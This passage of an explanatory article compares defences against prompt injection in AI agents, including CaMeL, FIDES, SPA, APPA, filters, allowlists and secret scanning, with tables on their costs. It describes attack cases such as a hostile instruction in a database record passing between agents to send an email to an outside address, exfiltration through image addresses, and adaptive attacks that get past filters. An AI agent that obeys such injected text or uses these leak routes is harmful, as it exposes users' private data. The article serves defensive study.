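Their main finding is that CaMeL's protection can fail when agents delegate work to other agents. In one demonstration, all three agents used CaMeL, and the user asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. One applicant's record contained a hostile instruction. A coordinating agent got the records from a database agent and put the summary into its message to a notification agent. The notification agent treated the whole message as its user's request, so its planning model read the instruction and added an email to an outside address. The researchers call it boundary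 laundering when text that one agent handled as untrusted data becomes a trusted request to the next. Their extension, multi-CaMeL, sends requests and data separately and rejects any request that contains tool output.

The 2026 system SPA stores results with their labels and shows later planning steps only a description of each result. In the Monday and Tuesday example, the attacker's account number would still carry its untrusted label when the agent came to pay. *CaMeLoT* (2026) criticizes CaMeL's policies as "temporally local" and uses temporal logic, which can express rules about the order of events, such as "no public comment after reading a contract".

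### What these systems cost in completed tasks

The table gives the main measurements. The tests use different models, tasks and attacks, so its rows don't rank the systems.

| System and test | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|
| FIDES with GPT-4o, on AgentDojo | 152 for an ordinary agent, 0 for FIDES | 84.3% for an ordinary agent, 50.0% for FIDES (average of four settings) |
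| SPA, on AgentDojo | 0.0% with label checks | 53.0% without label checks, 29.0% with them |
| CaMeL in each of several agents, average of five models | 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with it | 21.6 percentage points fewer with CaMeL, on a separate set of 112 tasks |
| Multi-CaMeL, same tests | 0.0% | A further 3.2 points fewer |
| APPA with three models, on two benchmarks | 0 in 1,320 runs | 64.2% to 91%, depending on the model and test |
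| SAMOS, on the GitHub attack | Blocked | Not measured |

FIDES and SPA each failed more than 40 per cent of the tasks that the unprotected versions completed. Many of these failures were intended, because the agent is meant to refuse to act on untrusted text. AgentDojo's banking tasks, for example, often ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, such as pay a bill. Girrens and Wang likewise found that SPA mostly rejected plans in which a tool's output determined a consequential action, though people want agents for this kind of work.

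Hiding data in variables lets an agent complete some tasks that label checks would otherwise block. When Costa and colleagues added label checks to an ordinary agent without variables, it completed 41.9 per cent of tasks on average, about 8 points less than FIDES. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger model for its time, FIDES's advantage rose to 16 points.

CaMeL also reduces task completion less with better models. The drop was 13.4 points instead of 21.6 for Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, the strongest models that Peters-Gill and colleagues tested. Tallam and Miller report that CaMeL completes 67 per cent of AgentDojo tasks, but they take that figure from the original evaluation, not from their own tests. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran CaMeL without any data policies, so their results show only the effect of protecting the plan. A deployment with strict policies would probably complete fewer tasks.

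GPT-5.5 resisted every attack in that test even without CaMeL, so adding CaMeL made the model less useful with no measurable gain in security. Kravchenko and colleagues left AgentDojo out of their tests because recent models already resist its attacks. The case for these systems therefore depends less on benchmark scores than on the guarantee, which also covers attacks nobody has thought of yet. Whether the guarantee justifies losing a sixth or a third of an agent's tasks depends on how much harm a leak would do.

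APPA's results look the most practical, with some caveats. Its 1,320 runs repeated 44 task designs, and the researchers wrote the policies for both APPA and the FIDES configurations they compared it with. On corporate tasks, 26 to 35 per cent of attacks succeeded against those configurations, but they had no rules for exact recipients or required approvals, which the tasks depended on. The tests that switched off parts of APPA are more informative. With GPT-5.6 Luna, full APPA completed 88 per cent of the corporate tasks, compared with 35 per cent without the list of ways forward and 56.5 per cent without disposable copies. No attacks succeeded against any of these versions, so the recovery features account for much of APPA's usefulness.

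Developers can use labels in real products. Microsoft documents FIDES features in its Agent Framework, a toolkit for developers, and Kravchenko and colleagues built their comparison from those features. This doesn't show how many developers use labels.

### Filters, allowlists and secret blocking

Three weaker measures are easier to add, and none of them requires a new kind of agent.

Injection filters, which inspect text before the model reads it, can catch careless attacks but often miss ones that an attacker keeps rewording. Willison summarizes a study of 12 published defences, several of them filters, in which adaptive attacks got past most of the defences more than 90 per cent of the time.

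Filters on outgoing text can miss private data. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* points out that pattern searches miss paraphrases and coded references. Comparing the overall meaning of the outgoing text with the private records fails when the text is short. The paper's own checker is a language model that is given every private record the agent has read and answers only whether the text is safe. It can catch paraphrases, but it can also make mistakes, whereas a label check doesn't depend on understanding the text.

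An allowlist limits the agent to approved recipients or websites. Meta suggests a strict version for web access, in which the agent opens only addresses that a trusted source has returned and never one it has written itself. This stops an agent from sending out stolen data in an image's address. But an allowlist doesn't control what the agent sends to an approved destination. If Maya approves her issue tracker so that the agent can answer bug reports, the agent can also post her invoice there. The storage service that leaked data between ChatGPT accounts was also a permitted destination.

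GitHub's remote MCP server scans the inputs of tool calls that involve public repositories and blocks a call if it finds an exposed secret, such as an access key, though the user can override the block. The feature is free on all plans. GitHub says the scan won't stop leaks of other data or leaks through channels it doesn't cover. The personal details leaked in the GitHub attack weren't formatted like keys, so the scan probably wouldn't have blocked them.

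### Which step each measure stops

Maya can separate her sessions herself, but most of the other measures need a developer or an administrator. They work best together because they stop an attack at different steps.

| Measure | Attack step it stops | What it misses | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Separate sessions, or the Rule of Two | Private data, hostile text and an outbound channel coming together | False answers, harmful changes, and text carried over by memory | Tasks that need all three require approval |
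| One repository per session | Reading private data in another repository | Leaks through other servers or within one repository | No work across repositories |
| Information-flow labels | The outbound call that would disclose private data | Wrong labels, and clues from the pattern of calls | The context soon becomes too restricted for many tasks |
| SAMOS gateway | Reading private data after public text | Malicious servers, and anything that bypasses the gateway | Manual labelling, and no private reads after public ones |
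| CaMeL | Hostile text changing the agent's plan | False data within the plan, unless a policy covers it | Fewer completed tasks, more model calls and a policy for each tool |
| Injection filter | Hostile text entering the context | Reworded attacks | False alarms |
| Destination allowlist | Sending data to an unapproved address | Leaks through approved destinations | Someone has to approve each new destination |
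| Secret blocking | Posting recognizable keys in public repositories | All other private data | An occasional harmless call blocked |
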